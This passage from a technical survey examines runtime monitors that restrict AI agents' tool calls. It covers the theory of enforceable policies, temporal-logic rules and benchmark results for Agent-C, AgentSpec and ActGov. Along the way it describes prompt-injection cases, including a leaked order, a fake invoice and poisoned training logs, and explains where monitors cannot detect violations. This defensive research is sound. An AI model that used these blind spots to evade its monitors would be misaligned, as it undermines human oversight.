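Dang is the paper's only author, so the same person built Praetor, prepared the scenarios and set up the competing firewall. Dang did not release the code and traces with the paper, but promised them on acceptance or request. The details of the setup therefore matter, and several are hard to reconcile with the original sources.

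*Agent Security Bench (ASB)* (Zhang, Huang and colleagues, 2024) differs a good deal from Dang's description. It tested ten agents, including a system administrator and an academic researcher, but no customer-service agent or travel planner. Each agent has two ordinary tools, which take no arguments, and an attack counts as successful when the agent uses a separate tool supplied by the attacker. Allowing each agent only its two ordinary tools would therefore stop every attack in the original benchmark. The benchmark could not test Praetor's argument limits, and it would provide little evidence about the value of tracking the order of tool calls.

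Dang's agents have between 15 and 64 tools, with arguments, so the test must be a substantial adaptation of the benchmark. Without a defence, attacks succeeded 79.0 percent of the time on average, compared with 46.9 percent across 13 language models in the original. Dang doesn't name the model that ran the agent. The 2.2 percent therefore applies only to Dang's scenarios, and readers can't compare it with other scores on the benchmark.

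The version of Aegis is also uncertain. Dang says it includes a statistical profile of the past seven days' behaviour, but Yuan and colleagues list behavioural profiling as future work. The two papers also link to different code repositories. Dang's customer-service results are inconsistent too. Dang gives a database-reading tool as an example of a tool missing from the benign traces, but elsewhere counts three permitted paths that end in it.

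The comparison still supports the narrower claim that tracking the order of calls stops some attacks that a checker misses when it examines each call separately, but the size of the advantage is much less certain.

### Poisoned and mistaken logs

Praetor assumes that every trace it learns from is benign. An attacker who can influence the agent while the operator collects logs could add harmful sequences or gradually widen the accepted range of an argument. The finished state machine would then permit the attack.

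Dang's remedy is to collect the logs in an isolated test environment, with operator-written prompts. Forrest and colleagues similarly chose artificial messages for sendmail. In a follow-up paper, *Lightweight Intrusion Detection for Networked Operating Systems*, Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji collected normal behaviour both artificially and from live use. Live logs cover what people really ask for but may contain attacks, which are easier to keep out of artificial logs. However, artificial logs may leave out unusual requests, and most of the benign calls that Praetor wrongly blocked belonged to rare sequences.

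An agent can also contaminate its logs without an attacker, for example by skipping authentication. If a few such runs passed as normal, their transitions could meet Praetor's threshold of three. To remove them, a reviewer has to compare the traces with the shop's rules, so the operator still needs a policy, even if it is unwritten.

### Usual and permitted behaviour

Even clean logs can't fully determine the policy. A trace shows that one sequence was acceptable, but a sequence missing from the logs may be forbidden or may just not have been needed yet. Gold proved in 1967 that for broad classes of rules, including the class of all rules that finite-state machines can express, no method can always identify the right rule from permitted examples alone. A learner therefore needs some assumption about the missing sequences, and Praetor treats them as forbidden.

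Cho and colleagues tested whether a run's fit to the machine predicts its success. They used AUROC, the probability that a randomly chosen failed run receives a higher risk score than a randomly chosen successful one. A score based only on fit gave about 0.50, no better than chance. A classifier trained on both successful and failed runs reached up to 0.94. It also used details such as how often a run visited each state and how improbable its transitions were. Such a score could alert a person to a suspicious run, but it doesn't establish which rule the agent broke.

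The same researchers tested their machines on real traces that they had altered by one step. The machines rejected at least 77 percent of traces with a step replaced, inserted or swapped, but in one dataset they rejected only 61 percent of traces with a step removed. Removing a step can turn one valid run into another. For example, the shop's second run without the refund is identical to its first. The lower rate for removed steps matters because many safety rules forbid skipping a step.

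*Learning Correct Behavior from Examples* (2026) addresses part of this problem by extracting the states that every successful run must pass through. Other learned state machines don't separate these from optional states. In the three shop traces, the method would mark `issue_refund` as optional and both `verify_customer` and `read_order` as essential, although answering a general question doesn't require `read_order`. The traces can't show which of the two steps marked essential the shop actually requires.

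*Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Iqbal and colleagues, 2026) learns from harmful runs as well as benign ones. It uses not only the order of tools but also where each argument came from, such as the user's request or an outside document. It sends unclear cases to a language model, which compares the proposed action with the request. In replays of recorded runs from two benchmarks, it blocked 94.3 percent of successful injections and allowed 95.1 percent of benign runs.

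Checking where an argument came from can help with the leaked order, since the attacker's address came from a delivery note rather than from the customer. But a user may ask the agent to act on an outside document, for instance to pay a bill from a file. Sequeira and colleagues acknowledge that their system won't reliably stop a realistic fake invoice containing the attacker's account number. The sequence of calls is the same as for a legitimate payment, and the account number comes from the file the user told the agent to use.

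## Which rules a runtime monitor can enforce

No transition table can enforce every rule, whether a developer writes it or software learns it, because the monitor decides on each call using only what has happened so far in the run. Schneider proved in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) that a monitor that observes a single run of a program and can only stop it can enforce only safety properties. These are rules whose violations always show up after finitely many steps and can't be repaired by later steps. The limit arises because such a monitor has no information about what the program will do next or could have done instead.

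To enforce a rule, a monitor must prevent every violation (soundness) and leave compliant runs unchanged (transparency). A monitor that blocks every action is sound but not transparent.

### Schneider's three conditions

Some programs never stop, so a trace σ may be finite or infinite. Let Π be the set of all traces that a program can produce. P(Π) means that the program satisfies the rule, and P̂(σ) means that the single trace σ does. Schneider derives three conditions from what the monitor can observe and do:

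1. The rule judges each trace on its own: P(Π) holds exactly when P̂(σ) holds for every σ in Π. The monitor observes one run and has no others to compare it with.
2. Once a finite trace τ breaks the rule, every continuation breaks it too: if ¬P̂(τ), then ¬P̂(τσ) for every σ. The program might stop right after τ, so the monitor can't allow τ in the hope that a later step will repair it.
3. Every violation shows up after finitely many steps: if ¬P̂(σ), then ¬P̂(σ[..i]) for some i, where σ[..i] is the first i steps of σ. Otherwise the monitor would never reach a point at which it should stop the run.

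A rule that meets all three conditions is a safety property. A liveness property is a rule that every finite trace can be extended to satisfy, meaning that for every finite τ there is some σ such that P̂(τσ). Liveness properties typically require something to happen eventually. Alpern and Schneider proved in the 1980s that every rule about single traces combines a safety property with a liveness property.

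Some safety properties are unenforceable, so the converse of Schneider's result is false. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker proved in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005) that a monitor able to halt the program before any action can enforce a safety property exactly when two conditions hold. An algorithm must be able to decide whether a finite trace complies, and the empty trace must comply, because a monitor that stops a program at the outset leaves an empty trace. Practical rules usually meet both conditions. Schneider's own counterexample is more important for agents because it involves the passing of time, which no monitor can halt.

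### A machine for "no Send after FileRead"

Schneider writes safety properties as security automata. These are state machines that stop the program when it attempts a step for which the current state has no transition. One of them prevents a program from sending messages after it has read a file:

| Current state | Step | Next state |
|---|---|---|
| No file read | anything except FileRead | No file read |
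| No file read | FileRead | File read |
| File read | anything except Send | File read |

The program can send messages until it reads a file. After that, the automaton has no transition for Send, so it stops the program at the next attempt to send.

This works only if "Send" covers every way of sending a message and "FileRead" every way of reading a file. Schneider warns that some of these may be deep inside the program. An agent with a shell, for example, can send data without calling `send_email`.

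### Testing the shop's rules

The next table applies Schneider's result to one of the shop's existing rules and three possible new ones.

| Rule | Shortest violation | Can a halting monitor enforce it? |
|---|---|---|
| Verify the customer before reading an order | `read_order` without an earlier match | Yes |
| Email every refunded customer eventually | None, since an email could still follow | No |
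| Email the customer within five calls of a refund | A refund, then five calls without the email | Yes, by stopping the run |
| Email the customer within five minutes of a refund | A refund, then five minutes without the email | No, because the clock keeps running |

The five-call rule is a safety property, but enforcing it may not help Ana. Suppose the agent refunds her order, makes four calls without emailing her, and then proposes a fifth that isn't the email. The monitor stops the run before the fifth call, so the agent has complied with the rule even though Ana never gets an email. A monitor that can only halt a run can't make the agent take a required action. Schneider gives a similar example of a seller who has taken a customer's money. A monitor can block every action except providing the service, but it can't stop the seller from doing nothing.

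Instead of halting, the shop's monitor could return an error and deny every other call until the agent sends the email. He and colleagues found that agents often recover from such errors, but the monitor can't guarantee that they will. Schneider notes that notifying a program fails for some limits on steps, because the program's response is another step. The shop can avoid this problem by counting only calls that run.

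The five-call rule is a safety property only if the shop does not count a run that ends early as a violation. Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, in *More Enforceable Security Policies* (2002), discuss a rule that a program must release a resource within ten steps. They count a run that ends after eight steps without a release as a violation, even though the program could still have released the resource in the ninth step, so they classify the rule as part safety and part liveness. If the shop also counted such runs as violations, a halting monitor could ensure compliance only by refusing every refund, because any run might end right after one.

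### Actions a monitor can observe but not prevent

The five-minute rule fails for another reason. After a refund, the deadline passes even if the monitor stops the agent. Schneider makes this point about a limit on how long a user may wait for a resource. A monitor can enforce the limit if it is measured in program steps, but not if it is measured in seconds.

Basin, Jugé and colleagues, in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (2012), extend the theory to cover such cases. They separate controllable actions, which the monitor can prevent, from actions it can only observe. Their two main examples both involve a clock:

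- After a failed login, nobody may log in for three time units. A monitor can enforce this rule by observing the failure and the clock, then blocking login attempts until the time has passed.
- The system must deliver within three time units of a request, unless it stops first. A monitor can't enforce this rule, because the step that breaks it is a clock tick.

In general, a monitor can enforce a rule only if it can prevent the action that makes a violation final. Let U be the set of traces that can occur, O the set of actions that the monitor can only observe, and P the set of compliant traces. Basin and colleagues require that every trace σ in U but outside P has a prefix σ[..i] that does not end in an action from O and has no continuation in both P and U. If O is empty and every trace can occur, this is the ordinary definition of safety.

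They prove that a rule is enforceable exactly when it meets this condition, the empty trace complies with it, and an algorithm can decide whether a finite trace still has a compliant continuation. The proof assumes that an algorithm can also decide which finite traces can occur. For rules written as finite-state machines, software can check enforceability before deployment and build the monitor. For rules written as machines with an unlimited stack, no algorithm can decide enforceability in every case.

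An agent's monitor can observe many actions that it can't block, such as a customer's reply, a courier's delay or a manager's change to someone's permissions. The same is true of each web search that Anthropic runs on its own servers, although the application can leave the search tool out of its next request to the model.

### Why information flow needs more than one run

Schneider's first condition excludes many rules about secrecy. An information-flow rule forbids an agent's output from depending on certain data. One run can't show whether the output depends on the data, because that requires knowing what the agent would have output if the data had been different. Clarkson and Schneider's *Hyperproperties* (2009) introduced the term "hyperproperty" for a rule about sets of runs.

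*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that arranges a meeting. The assistant is allowed to reveal when its user is free, but not why the user is busy. In one run, the user is busy with an ordinary meeting and the assistant offers slot 10. In another, the same slots are free, but the user is busy with a confidential interview and the assistant offers slot 11. Each offer is permissible on its own. But if the assistant offered a different slot because of the interview, it has leaked information about the interview.

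The paper's rule compares two runs t and t′:

```
if   low(t) = low(t′)  and  D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′))
then α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′))
```

Here `low` is the task and other non-secret input, `hi` is the sensitive data, and `D` is the part of that data the assistant may use. `obs` is what the assistant discloses, and `α` keeps only the details that matter to the policy, such as the slots offered. Any single run satisfies the rule, because its output equals itself. A monitor that judges runs separately and never raises a false alarm therefore can't detect any violation, whatever model or algorithm it uses.

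Pandey and colleagues tested this with nine language models as judges. When the judges saw one call at a time, eight of them blocked nothing in 30 trials each. The ninth blocked a call in three trials, compared with one trial when the runs were harmless. When the same models saw both runs together, eight flagged the violation in all 30 trials and Llama-4-Maverick did so in 17. The judges had lacked information when they saw only one call at a time, although Llama-4-Maverick missed some violations even when it saw both runs.

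In practice, monitors enforce a stricter rule, such as "no Send after FileRead", that prevents the leak but also blocks harmless runs. In the shop, this rule would ban every email after `read_order`, which would stop the leaked order but also Ana's refund confirmation. Taint tracking, a less strict method, labels sensitive values and blocks output derived from them. It would miss the leak in the calendar example, because the assistant offers a slot from the list it may share and the secret affects only which slot it picks.

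Comparing runs also has limits. A language model's output can vary by chance, so two different offers don't prove a leak. An auditor has to repeat the task many times with different secrets, and even then the evidence is statistical. Pandey and colleagues ran 80 such episodes with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and found no leak, which is compatible with a leak rate of up to 3.7 percent. Their first analysis had reported a leak, but the program had counted a chance difference in wording when the offered slots were the same.

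A developer can instead prevent the leak by generating the reply only from data the assistant may reveal, in this case the list of free slots, so the secret can't influence the offer. This requires an extra model run, and the reply can't benefit from the excluded data.

However, a monitor can check some privacy rules from a single run. In another calendar test by Pandey and colleagues, Qwen3-30B disclosed more in total than the user had agreed to in 22 of 60 runs, although each disclosure was permissible on its own. With a guard that compared each call with the stated purpose, this still happened in 20 of 60 runs. A guard that tracked the total prevented it in every run and blocked none of the 120 harmless control runs. Later calls can't undo a disclosure that exceeds the total, so this rule is a safety property.

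### Holding back and inserting actions

A monitor can enforce more rules if it can do more than permit an action or stop the program. Ligatti and colleagues study edit automata, which can also suppress an action the program attempts or insert one it does not attempt. For each state and attempted action, the transition function gives a new state and either an action to insert or an instruction to drop the attempted one.

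Such a monitor can hold back actions until it knows that the whole sequence complies. Suppose the shop wants every refund to be followed by an email:

| Agent's call | Result the monitor reports | What actually happens |
|---|---|---|
| `issue_refund(1042, £60)` | refunded | nothing yet |
| `send_email("ana@example.com", …)` | sent | the refund runs, then the email goes out |

If the agent never writes the email, the refund never runs, so no violation takes effect outside the system. Enforcing this rule goes beyond enforcing safety properties, because a refund without an email breaks the rule only until the email follows.

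Ligatti and colleagues prove that edit automata can enforce any renewal property, provided that the empty trace complies and an algorithm can decide whether any given finite trace complies. A rule is a renewal property if an infinite trace complies exactly when it keeps returning to points at which everything so far complies. Renewal properties include every safety property and some liveness properties, such as the rule that a program that does anything must eventually perform an audit.

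If all runs are finite, every rule about single runs is a renewal property. But suppose an agent serves customers indefinitely and must eventually email everyone it refunds. It might refund Ana and Ben, email Ana, refund Carla, email Ben and so on. Everybody eventually gets an email, but after the first refund somebody is always waiting for one. A monitor that releases actions only once nobody is waiting would hold back the refunds forever.

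The refund table also shows a practical problem, because the monitor reports a refund that has not happened. If the payment service later declines it, the agent has written Ana's email based on a false result and may already have told her in the chat that the shop has paid. The monitor can't delay other calls at all. For example, it can't invent a result for `read_order`, because the agent needs the contents of the order before it can continue. Ligatti and colleagues acknowledge this limitation with the example of a program that sends an email and then acts on the reply, which can't arrive unless the email is actually sent.

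Most monitors for agents therefore decide on each call when it arrives. Ray proves that such a gate, if it must leave compliant runs unchanged, can enforce only safety properties. For example, it can't enforce the rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment, because if it allows a payment, the confirmation may never come, and if it blocks the payment, it interferes with runs in which the confirmation would have come. Letting the gate replace a forbidden call with a permitted one doesn't enlarge the set of rules it can enforce, though it may help the agent finish its task. Ray attributes the difference between what gates and edit automata can enforce to irreversible actions, but it also depends on whether an action can be delayed, since an irreversible payment can still wait in a queue if nothing needs its result yet.

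Suppression suits text better because the system doesn't have to act as if the reader has already received the withheld text. *Withholding the Completing Chunk* (2026) describes a filter that checks a language model's output as it streams and can withhold a piece of it.

A monitor that inserts actions can supply a missing one when a run ends. To mark the end of a run, Bauer and colleagues suggest adding a stop event to every program, with a timeout in case the program hangs. An agent's application can already detect the end, because the model finishes without requesting another tool. If the agent has refunded Ana but not emailed her by then, the monitor could send the email itself.

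Inserting real actions carries more risk than blocking them, because a mistaken insertion can send a false message or pay money that nobody requested, whereas a mistaken block usually delays a task. In the double refund, the payment service's reply got lost, so a monitor that sent an automatic confirmation might tell Ana about a refund it couldn't verify. The monitor may also lack what it needs to act, as in Bauer and colleagues' example of a contract that requires another party's private key to sign. It would be safer for the shop's monitor to insert a task asking a member of staff to check the refund and write to Ana.

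Later models specify what a monitor can do with each action. In *Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control*, Khoury and Hallé (2015) arrange actions by how much control the monitor has over them. *Towards an Enforceable GDPR Specification* (2024) labels events as observable, suppressable or causable, depending on what the system lets the monitor do. In the shop, `issue_refund` could have all three labels, while Ana's reply is only observable. The labels describe only what is technically possible, so the shop still has to decide whether a monitor should ever issue a refund by itself.

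### Combining monitors

A team may prefer several small monitors to one large state machine, because people can understand and review each rule separately. Schneider shows that if a call must pass several halting monitors, together they enforce the conjunction of their rules.

When monitors return errors instead of halting, all of them should check a call before any of them updates its state. Otherwise, one monitor might permit a refund and record it before a second monitor denies it. The first would then hold a record of a refund that never ran and might refuse a legitimate attempt later.

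Correct monitors can also leave the agent with nothing useful to do. Suppose the shop adds two rules:

- Send no email after reading an order.
- After a refund, the next call must email the customer.

Each rule is enforceable on its own, but the two conflict because the agent has to read an order before refunding it. After the refund, the first monitor denies every email and the second denies everything else. Ana has her money, but the agent can't confirm the refund or make any other call. Both monitors have worked correctly, and the trace satisfies both rules. Schneider describes an extreme case in which combined rules permit no runs.

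If the machines have finitely many states, a developer can look for such dead ends before deployment. The combined machine has one state for each combination of the separate machines' states, and software can search it for reachable states with no permitted calls. To keep the agent out of the dead end at runtime, the monitors would have to look ahead, as shields do, and refuse the refund.

Edit automata are harder to combine, since one may insert an action that another forbids. Suppose one monitor bans emails after `read_order` and passes the calls it permits to a second monitor, which inserts a confirmation email after each refund. The inserted email never goes through the first monitor, so it breaks the ban. If the monitors run in the reverse order, the one that bans emails blocks the confirmation, and Ana doesn't get it. According to Bauer and colleagues, edit automata can safely run one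 after another if they handle separate sets of actions, but here both handle `send_email`.

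## Rules about order written in temporal logic

A developer who prefers several small rules to one large state machine can write each rule as a short formula in temporal logic, and software then turns the formula into a monitor. Amir Pnueli proposed linear temporal logic for reasoning about programs in 1977 and defined it for runs that never end. Because an agent's run ends, the version for finite traces that De Giacomo and Vardi set out in 2013 suits agents better.

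### Four operators

A formula starts from statements that are true or false at a single step, such as "the agent calls `read_order`". The connectives ¬ (not), ∨ (or) and → (if … then) combine statements about the same step, while temporal operators refer to other steps. At step i of a trace with n steps, four of these operators have the following meanings:

| Operator | Symbol | True at step i when |
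|---|---|---|
| Always | G φ | φ holds at every step from i to n |
| Eventually | F φ | φ holds at some step from i to n |
| Until | φ U ψ | ψ holds at some step j from i to n, and φ holds at every step from i to j − 1 |
| Once in the past | O φ | φ holds at some step from 1 to i |

The first three definitions follow *Monitoring Constraints and Metaconstraints with Temporal Logics on Finite Traces* (De Giacomo, De Masellis and colleagues, 2020), which is about monitoring business processes. The fourth follows *LTLf+ and PPLTL+* (Aminof, De Giacomo and colleagues, 2024). A trace satisfies a formula made of these operators if the formula is true at step 1. On a finite trace, "eventually" means that the required step must come before the trace ends.

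### From the verification rule to an automaton

The shop's agent must verify the customer before reading an order. Let `verified` be true at any step where `verify_customer` returns a match, and `read` at any step where the agent calls `read_order`. The rule is then:

```
G (read → O verified)
```

In words, whenever the agent reads an order, `verify_customer` must already have returned a match.

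*Runtime Verification for LTL and TLTL* (Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart, 2007) uses a similar formula for a program that must do nothing risky before it has initialised. For the shop, the formula would be `¬read U verified`. This is stricter than the shop intends, because "until" requires `verified` to become true at some point. If a customer only asked about opening hours and was never verified, the agent would break the rule even though it had read no order.

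In a conversation about one order, the rule "refund at most once" is written `G (refund → ¬Y O refund)`, where Y means "at the previous step". Without Y, the formula would forbid every refund, because O includes the current step.

Every formula over finite traces has an equivalent deterministic automaton, a state machine that accepts exactly the traces that satisfy the formula. *When Automata Meet Streams* (2026) uses this translation to plan robots' movements. For the verification rule, the construction has four steps:

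1. Store one bit for each temporal operator. The bit `seen` records whether a match has occurred and starts at 0. The bit `ok` records whether the rule has held so far and starts at 1.
2. After each step, set `seen` to 1 if the step was a match. Then set `ok` to 0 if the step was a read and `seen` is still 0.
3. List the combinations of the two bits, which gives four states.
4. Merge the two states in which `ok` is 0, because no later step can set it back to 1.

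| State | `seen`, `ok` | After a match | After `read_order` | After any other step | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Not verified | 0, 1 | Verified | Violated | Not verified | undecided |
| Verified | 1, 1 | Verified | Verified | Verified | satisfied |
| Violated | 0 or 1, 0 | Violated | Violated | Violated | violated |

With k temporal operators, this method produces at most 2ᵏ states, and a monitor can store the k bits without listing the states. According to Aminof and colleagues, automata for formulas about the future can grow doubly exponentially with the length of the formula, compared with a single exponential for formulas about the past. The two kinds of formula can express the same rules, but translating a formula from one kind to the other can make it exponentially longer. A formula that consists of G followed only by past operators always expresses a safety property, so a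 developer who keeps to this form avoids rules that a halting monitor can't enforce.

### Satisfied, violated and undecided

The verdicts in the table come from Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart. A rule is violated if no continuation of the trace can comply with it, satisfied if every continuation complies, and undecided otherwise. Software can work out the verdict for each state of the automaton in advance by checking which states can be reached from it.

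Their monitor only detects violations. To enforce the rule, the software has to check each call before running it and refuse any that would lead to Violated, as with the shop's state machine. Even while the verdict is undecided, the environment may still be able to force the agent to break the rule later. Shields address this problem.

Some rules stay undecided however long the run lasts, such as the rule that an email must follow every refund, `G (refund → F email)`. De Giacomo and colleagues therefore divide "undecided" into temporary violation and temporary satisfaction. After a refund, the email rule is temporarily violated, because ending the run there would break it. Once the agent sends the email, the rule is temporarily satisfied until the next refund. An application can use this distinction to decide whether the agent may end the conversation. The framework also allows rules that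 apply only after another rule has been permanently violated, such as a rule that the agent must alert a manager if it has read an order without verification.

### What order alone misses

Suppose Ana passes verification as customer 17 and then asks about order 2077, which belongs to Ben, customer 23. If the agent reads the order, the trace still satisfies the verification formula, because a match came before the read. Kamath and colleagues observed this failure in a test where an agent running on Qwen3-14B authenticated a customer named Sophia Hernandez and then tried to open Ethan Thomas's order.

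The rule has to compare the customer number that `verify_customer` returned with the owner of the requested order. True-or-false statements have the same problem as plain states, so first-order temporal logic adds variables that stand for any customer or order.

The monitor also needs the identity of the order's owner before the call runs. The shop's state machine gets this only from the result of `read_order`, but a monitor that looked up the owner separately could block the call before the model received Ben's details.

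### Agent-C's rules and solver

Agent-C, which Kamath and colleagues published in December 2025, supports both kinds of comparison. Its main construct, `before`, takes a call, a condition on that call, an earlier call that must have happened, and a condition relating the two. In slightly simplified notation, the shop's rule would be:

```
before(
  read_order(order = n), True,
  f: verify_customer(email = .*, postcode = .*),
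  output(f) == state(owner(n))
)
```

The pattern `.*` accepts any value, `output(f)` is what the earlier verification returned, and `state(owner(n))` is a read-only lookup that the tool's developer provides. Agent-C translates the rule into first-order logic:

```
for every time t:
  if    tool(t) = read_order
  then  there is an earlier time t′ with
        tool(t′) = verify_customer  and
        output(t′) = owner(order(t)), as looked up at time t
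```

Other constructs require a call to follow later (`after`) or two calls to occur in sequence (`seq`). A rule forbidding a sequence of two refunds on the same order would stop the double refund. In the paper's formal model, Agent-C adds a call to the trace before running it, so the rule would still block a second refund if the reply to the first were lost. However, it would also block a retry after the payment service had declined the first request.

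The language can't refer to the next step, so it can't require the call immediately after a refund to be an email. It also relates only two calls at a time and has no operator for adding up values across a series of calls. To cap the total of several partial refunds, the shop would need a lookup that returned the amount already refunded.

When the agent proposes a call, Agent-C appends it to the trace and combines the trace with the rules in one formula. It then asks Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true, whether any continuation of the trace could satisfy the rules. For the shop, the answers would be:

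| Trace so far | Proposed call | Can any continuation comply? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Empty | `read_order(1042)` | No, there is no earlier verification | Refuse |
| Ana verified as customer 17 | `read_order(2077)`, owner 23 | No, 17 ≠ 23 | Refuse |
| Ana verified as customer 17 | `read_order(1042)`, owner 17 | Yes | Run |

Agent-C permits a call when the verdict would be satisfied or undecided. Kamath and colleagues considered requiring every continuation of the trace to comply, but this would be too strict, since almost any trace could later break a rule. If Z3 gives no answer within two minutes, Agent-C discards the call.

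When the agent tries to finish, a second query checks whether the trace would comply if it ended there. An agent that still had to email Ana would fail this check, and Agent-C would end the run with an error status. The paper's main theorem states that every run that ends normally complies with the specification, so it doesn't cover runs that end in an error. The design also assumes that no other process changes the tools' data, but in a live shop an order could change between the lookup and the call.

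### Replacing a refused call

After a refusal, Agent-C makes the model try again, and how it does so depends on how much access the application has to the model. A language model writes a tool call as a series of tokens, which are words or parts of words, and assigns a probability to each possible next token. With an open-weight model, whose parameters are public, Agent-C can use these probabilities and intervene in the middle of a call. It has the model write the tool's name and then the arguments one by one. If an argument has the wrong type, Agent-C discards only that argument. If the solver refuses the finished call, Agent-C discards the call and generates another from the same point, with a penalty for repeating the violation.

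Providers of closed models don't expose all of these probabilities. For those models, Agent-C waits for the whole call, checks it and, if it rejects the call, sends the entire prompt again. In both versions, if every attempt fails, the model receives an error message that lists possible reasons. The printed algorithm for closed models doesn't change the prompt between attempts, and the tests ran Claude at temperature zero, where a model usually repeats its answer. Much of the recovery may therefore come from the error message.

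Both versions make the same solver check, so they give the same guarantee, but they differ in task completion and token use. Kamath and colleagues ran both on the open-weight model Qwen3-8B. The version that regenerates part of the output completed 42.1 percent of retail tasks and produced 359 tokens per model request, while the version that resends the prompt completed 36.5 percent and produced 600. In airline tasks, the completion rates were 39.3 and 36.7 percent, and the token counts were 415 and 899.

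### Results on τ-bench

The main tests used τ-bench (Yao et al., 2024), the predecessor of τ²-bench. A language model plays the customer, and the agent must follow a written policy while it looks up and changes records. The benchmark has 115 retail tasks and 50 airline tasks. Kamath and colleagues added 17 attacks in each domain, in which the customer pushes for something the policy forbids, such as returning somebody else's order. They also translated the policies into Agent-C's language.

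They report that conformance, the share of runs that broke no rule, rose from 77.4 to 100 percent for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 83.7 to 100 percent for GPT-5. Utility rose from 71.8 to 75.2 percent and from 66.1 to 70.6 percent, respectively. Anthropic released Claude Sonnet 4.5 in September 2025 and OpenAI released GPT-5 in August 2025, so the starting figures don't describe current models. The results by domain were as follows, where "harm" is the share of attacks in which the agent carried out the forbidden goal:

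| Model | Conformance, retail / airline | Utility, retail / airline | Harm, retail / airline |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 alone | 93.0% / 70.0% | 76.5% / 42.0% | 29.4% / 11.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 with Agent-C | 100% / 100% | 80.5% / 43.5% | 0% / 0% |
| GPT-5 alone | 91.9% / 71.3% | 71.0% / 38.0% | 3.9% / 2.0% |
| GPT-5 with Agent-C | 100% / 100% | 73.6% / 42.8% | 0% / 0% |

The headline conformance figures include the attacks. On the ordinary tasks alone, both unguarded models complied in about 86 percent of runs. The headline utility figures don't match the results by domain. When the domains are weighted by their number of tasks, utility rises from 66.1 to 69.3 percent for Claude and from 61.0 to 64.3 percent for GPT-5. These gains are similar to the reported ones, but the percentages themselves are lower.

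Part of the gain comes from how the paper defines utility. A run counts only if the agent finishes the task and breaks no rule, so an unguarded agent gets no credit for finishing a task if it breaks a rule along the way. Claude's gain on the airline tasks is also less than one task out of 50. Still, the results give no sign that enforcing the rules reduced the number of tasks these two models completed.

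Weaker models gained more from Agent-C. Qwen3-32B, an open-weight model from April 2025, complied in 37.7 percent of retail runs without Agent-C, and its utility rose from 25.5 to 53.3 percent with it. Across both domains, the average task took 44 percent longer with Agent-C.

### AgentSpec and ActGov

Kamath and colleagues also compared Agent-C with an earlier rule language, which Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, designed for agents that write code, control robots or drive cars. A later system from Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ActGov*, published in September 2026, targets prompt injection. The three systems differ mainly in how they express order and when they use a solver:

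| | Agent-C | AgentSpec | ActGov |
|---|---|---|---|
| Form of a rule | A relation between calls, their values and tool state | A trigger, conditions and a response | Conditions on a fixed set of labels |
| How it expresses order | `before`, `after`, `seq` | Only inside conditions written as program code | Labels that summarise earlier steps |
| When it checks | Before each call and at the end | Before an action, after a result or at the end | Before each call |
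| When it uses a solver | At each check | Never | Before deployment |

An AgentSpec rule for large refunds could look like this:

```
rule @inspect_large_refund
trigger issue_refund
check above_price
enforce user_inspection
end
```

The developer writes `above_price` as a Python function. Besides prompting the user, a rule can stop the agent, run a preset action or have the model reconsider. A rule that triggers on a call's result can act only after the call has run.

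In Kamath and colleagues' retail test with Qwen3-32B, AgentSpec reached 84.1 percent conformance and 37.4 percent utility, well below Agent-C. In the airline test, its conformance was 79.3 percent, but its utility was 38.7 percent, slightly higher than Agent-C's 35.8 percent. These figures depend on the rules that Kamath and colleagues wrote for AgentSpec. AgentSpec's Python functions receive the agent's history, so a developer could write one that searches for an earlier verification. However, the rule language would not help with this, and no solver could readily analyse the result.

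Wang and colleagues mostly tested single dangerous actions. With handwritten rules, a simulated robot carried out none of the hazardous tasks in ten categories, while its success on safe tasks fell from 58.6 to 54.3 percent. In the coding test, the rules flagged 333 of the 422 programs that the agent tried to run, or 79 percent. The share rises to 91 percent without two categories, totaling 58 programs, in which the agent's code did not contain the requested flaw. The researchers wrote the rules from descriptions of the same risks they tested, so the results show that the language can express such rules but are weaker evidence about unfamiliar hazards. Evaluating a rule's conditions took under three milliseconds on average.

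ActGov replaces the details of each call with labels that have only a few possible values. One label records where an argument came from, and another whether the user still has to approve an earlier step. Because the number of combinations is finite, Z3 can search all of them before deployment for a case where the rules permit something that a stated safety requirement forbids. If it finds one, a language model revises the rules. At run time, ordinary code applies the finished rules to the labels, but some of the labels come from a language model. If that model labelled the attacker's address in the leaked order as supplied by the customer, the rules could permit the email even though Z3 had checked them.

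Zhang, Peng and colleagues tested ActGov on AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark with tasks such as email and banking, and on AgentDyn, where legitimate tasks also require the agent to follow instructions from third parties. These are the results with the model DeepSeek-v4-pro, where utility refers to tasks without an attack:

| Test | Rules from | Attack success, undefended → ActGov | Utility, undefended → ActGov |
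|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | AgentDojo | 6.1% → 0% | 87.8% → 75.5% |
| AgentDyn | AgentDyn | 8.6% → 0.7% | 76.7% → 60.0% |
| AgentDojo | AgentDyn | 6.1% → 0% | 87.8% → 22.4% |
| AgentDyn | AgentDojo | 8.6% → 0% | 76.7% → 10.0% |

Even with rules made for the right benchmark, ActGov reduced this model's task completion rate by more percentage points than it reduced the attack success rate. That can be worthwhile if a successful attack does far more damage than an unfinished task. The last two rows show that the rules block most legitimate work in an unfamiliar setting.

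### When the formula differs from the policy

Agent-C's score of 100 percent means that its traces satisfied the written specification. It doesn't show that the specification matched the policy, or that the agent obeyed policy rules that can't be checked from its tool calls, such as the ban on subjective recommendations.

The airline and retail policies require the customer to say yes before the agent changes a record. To make this approval visible in the trace, Kamath and colleagues added a tool called `action_confirmed`, which the agent calls to report that the customer said yes. The specification can then require this call before a cancellation. But the agent makes the call itself, so the rule guarantees only that the agent reported a confirmation.

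Careful authors can also write a formula that is too loose. The retail policy allows a refund to the original payment method or to "an existing gift card". Kamath and colleagues' formula accepts the original method or any payment identifier that contains the text "gift_card". They call this a faithful translation, but the formula doesn't check that the card exists, so the refund tool would have to reject a refund to a made-up card.

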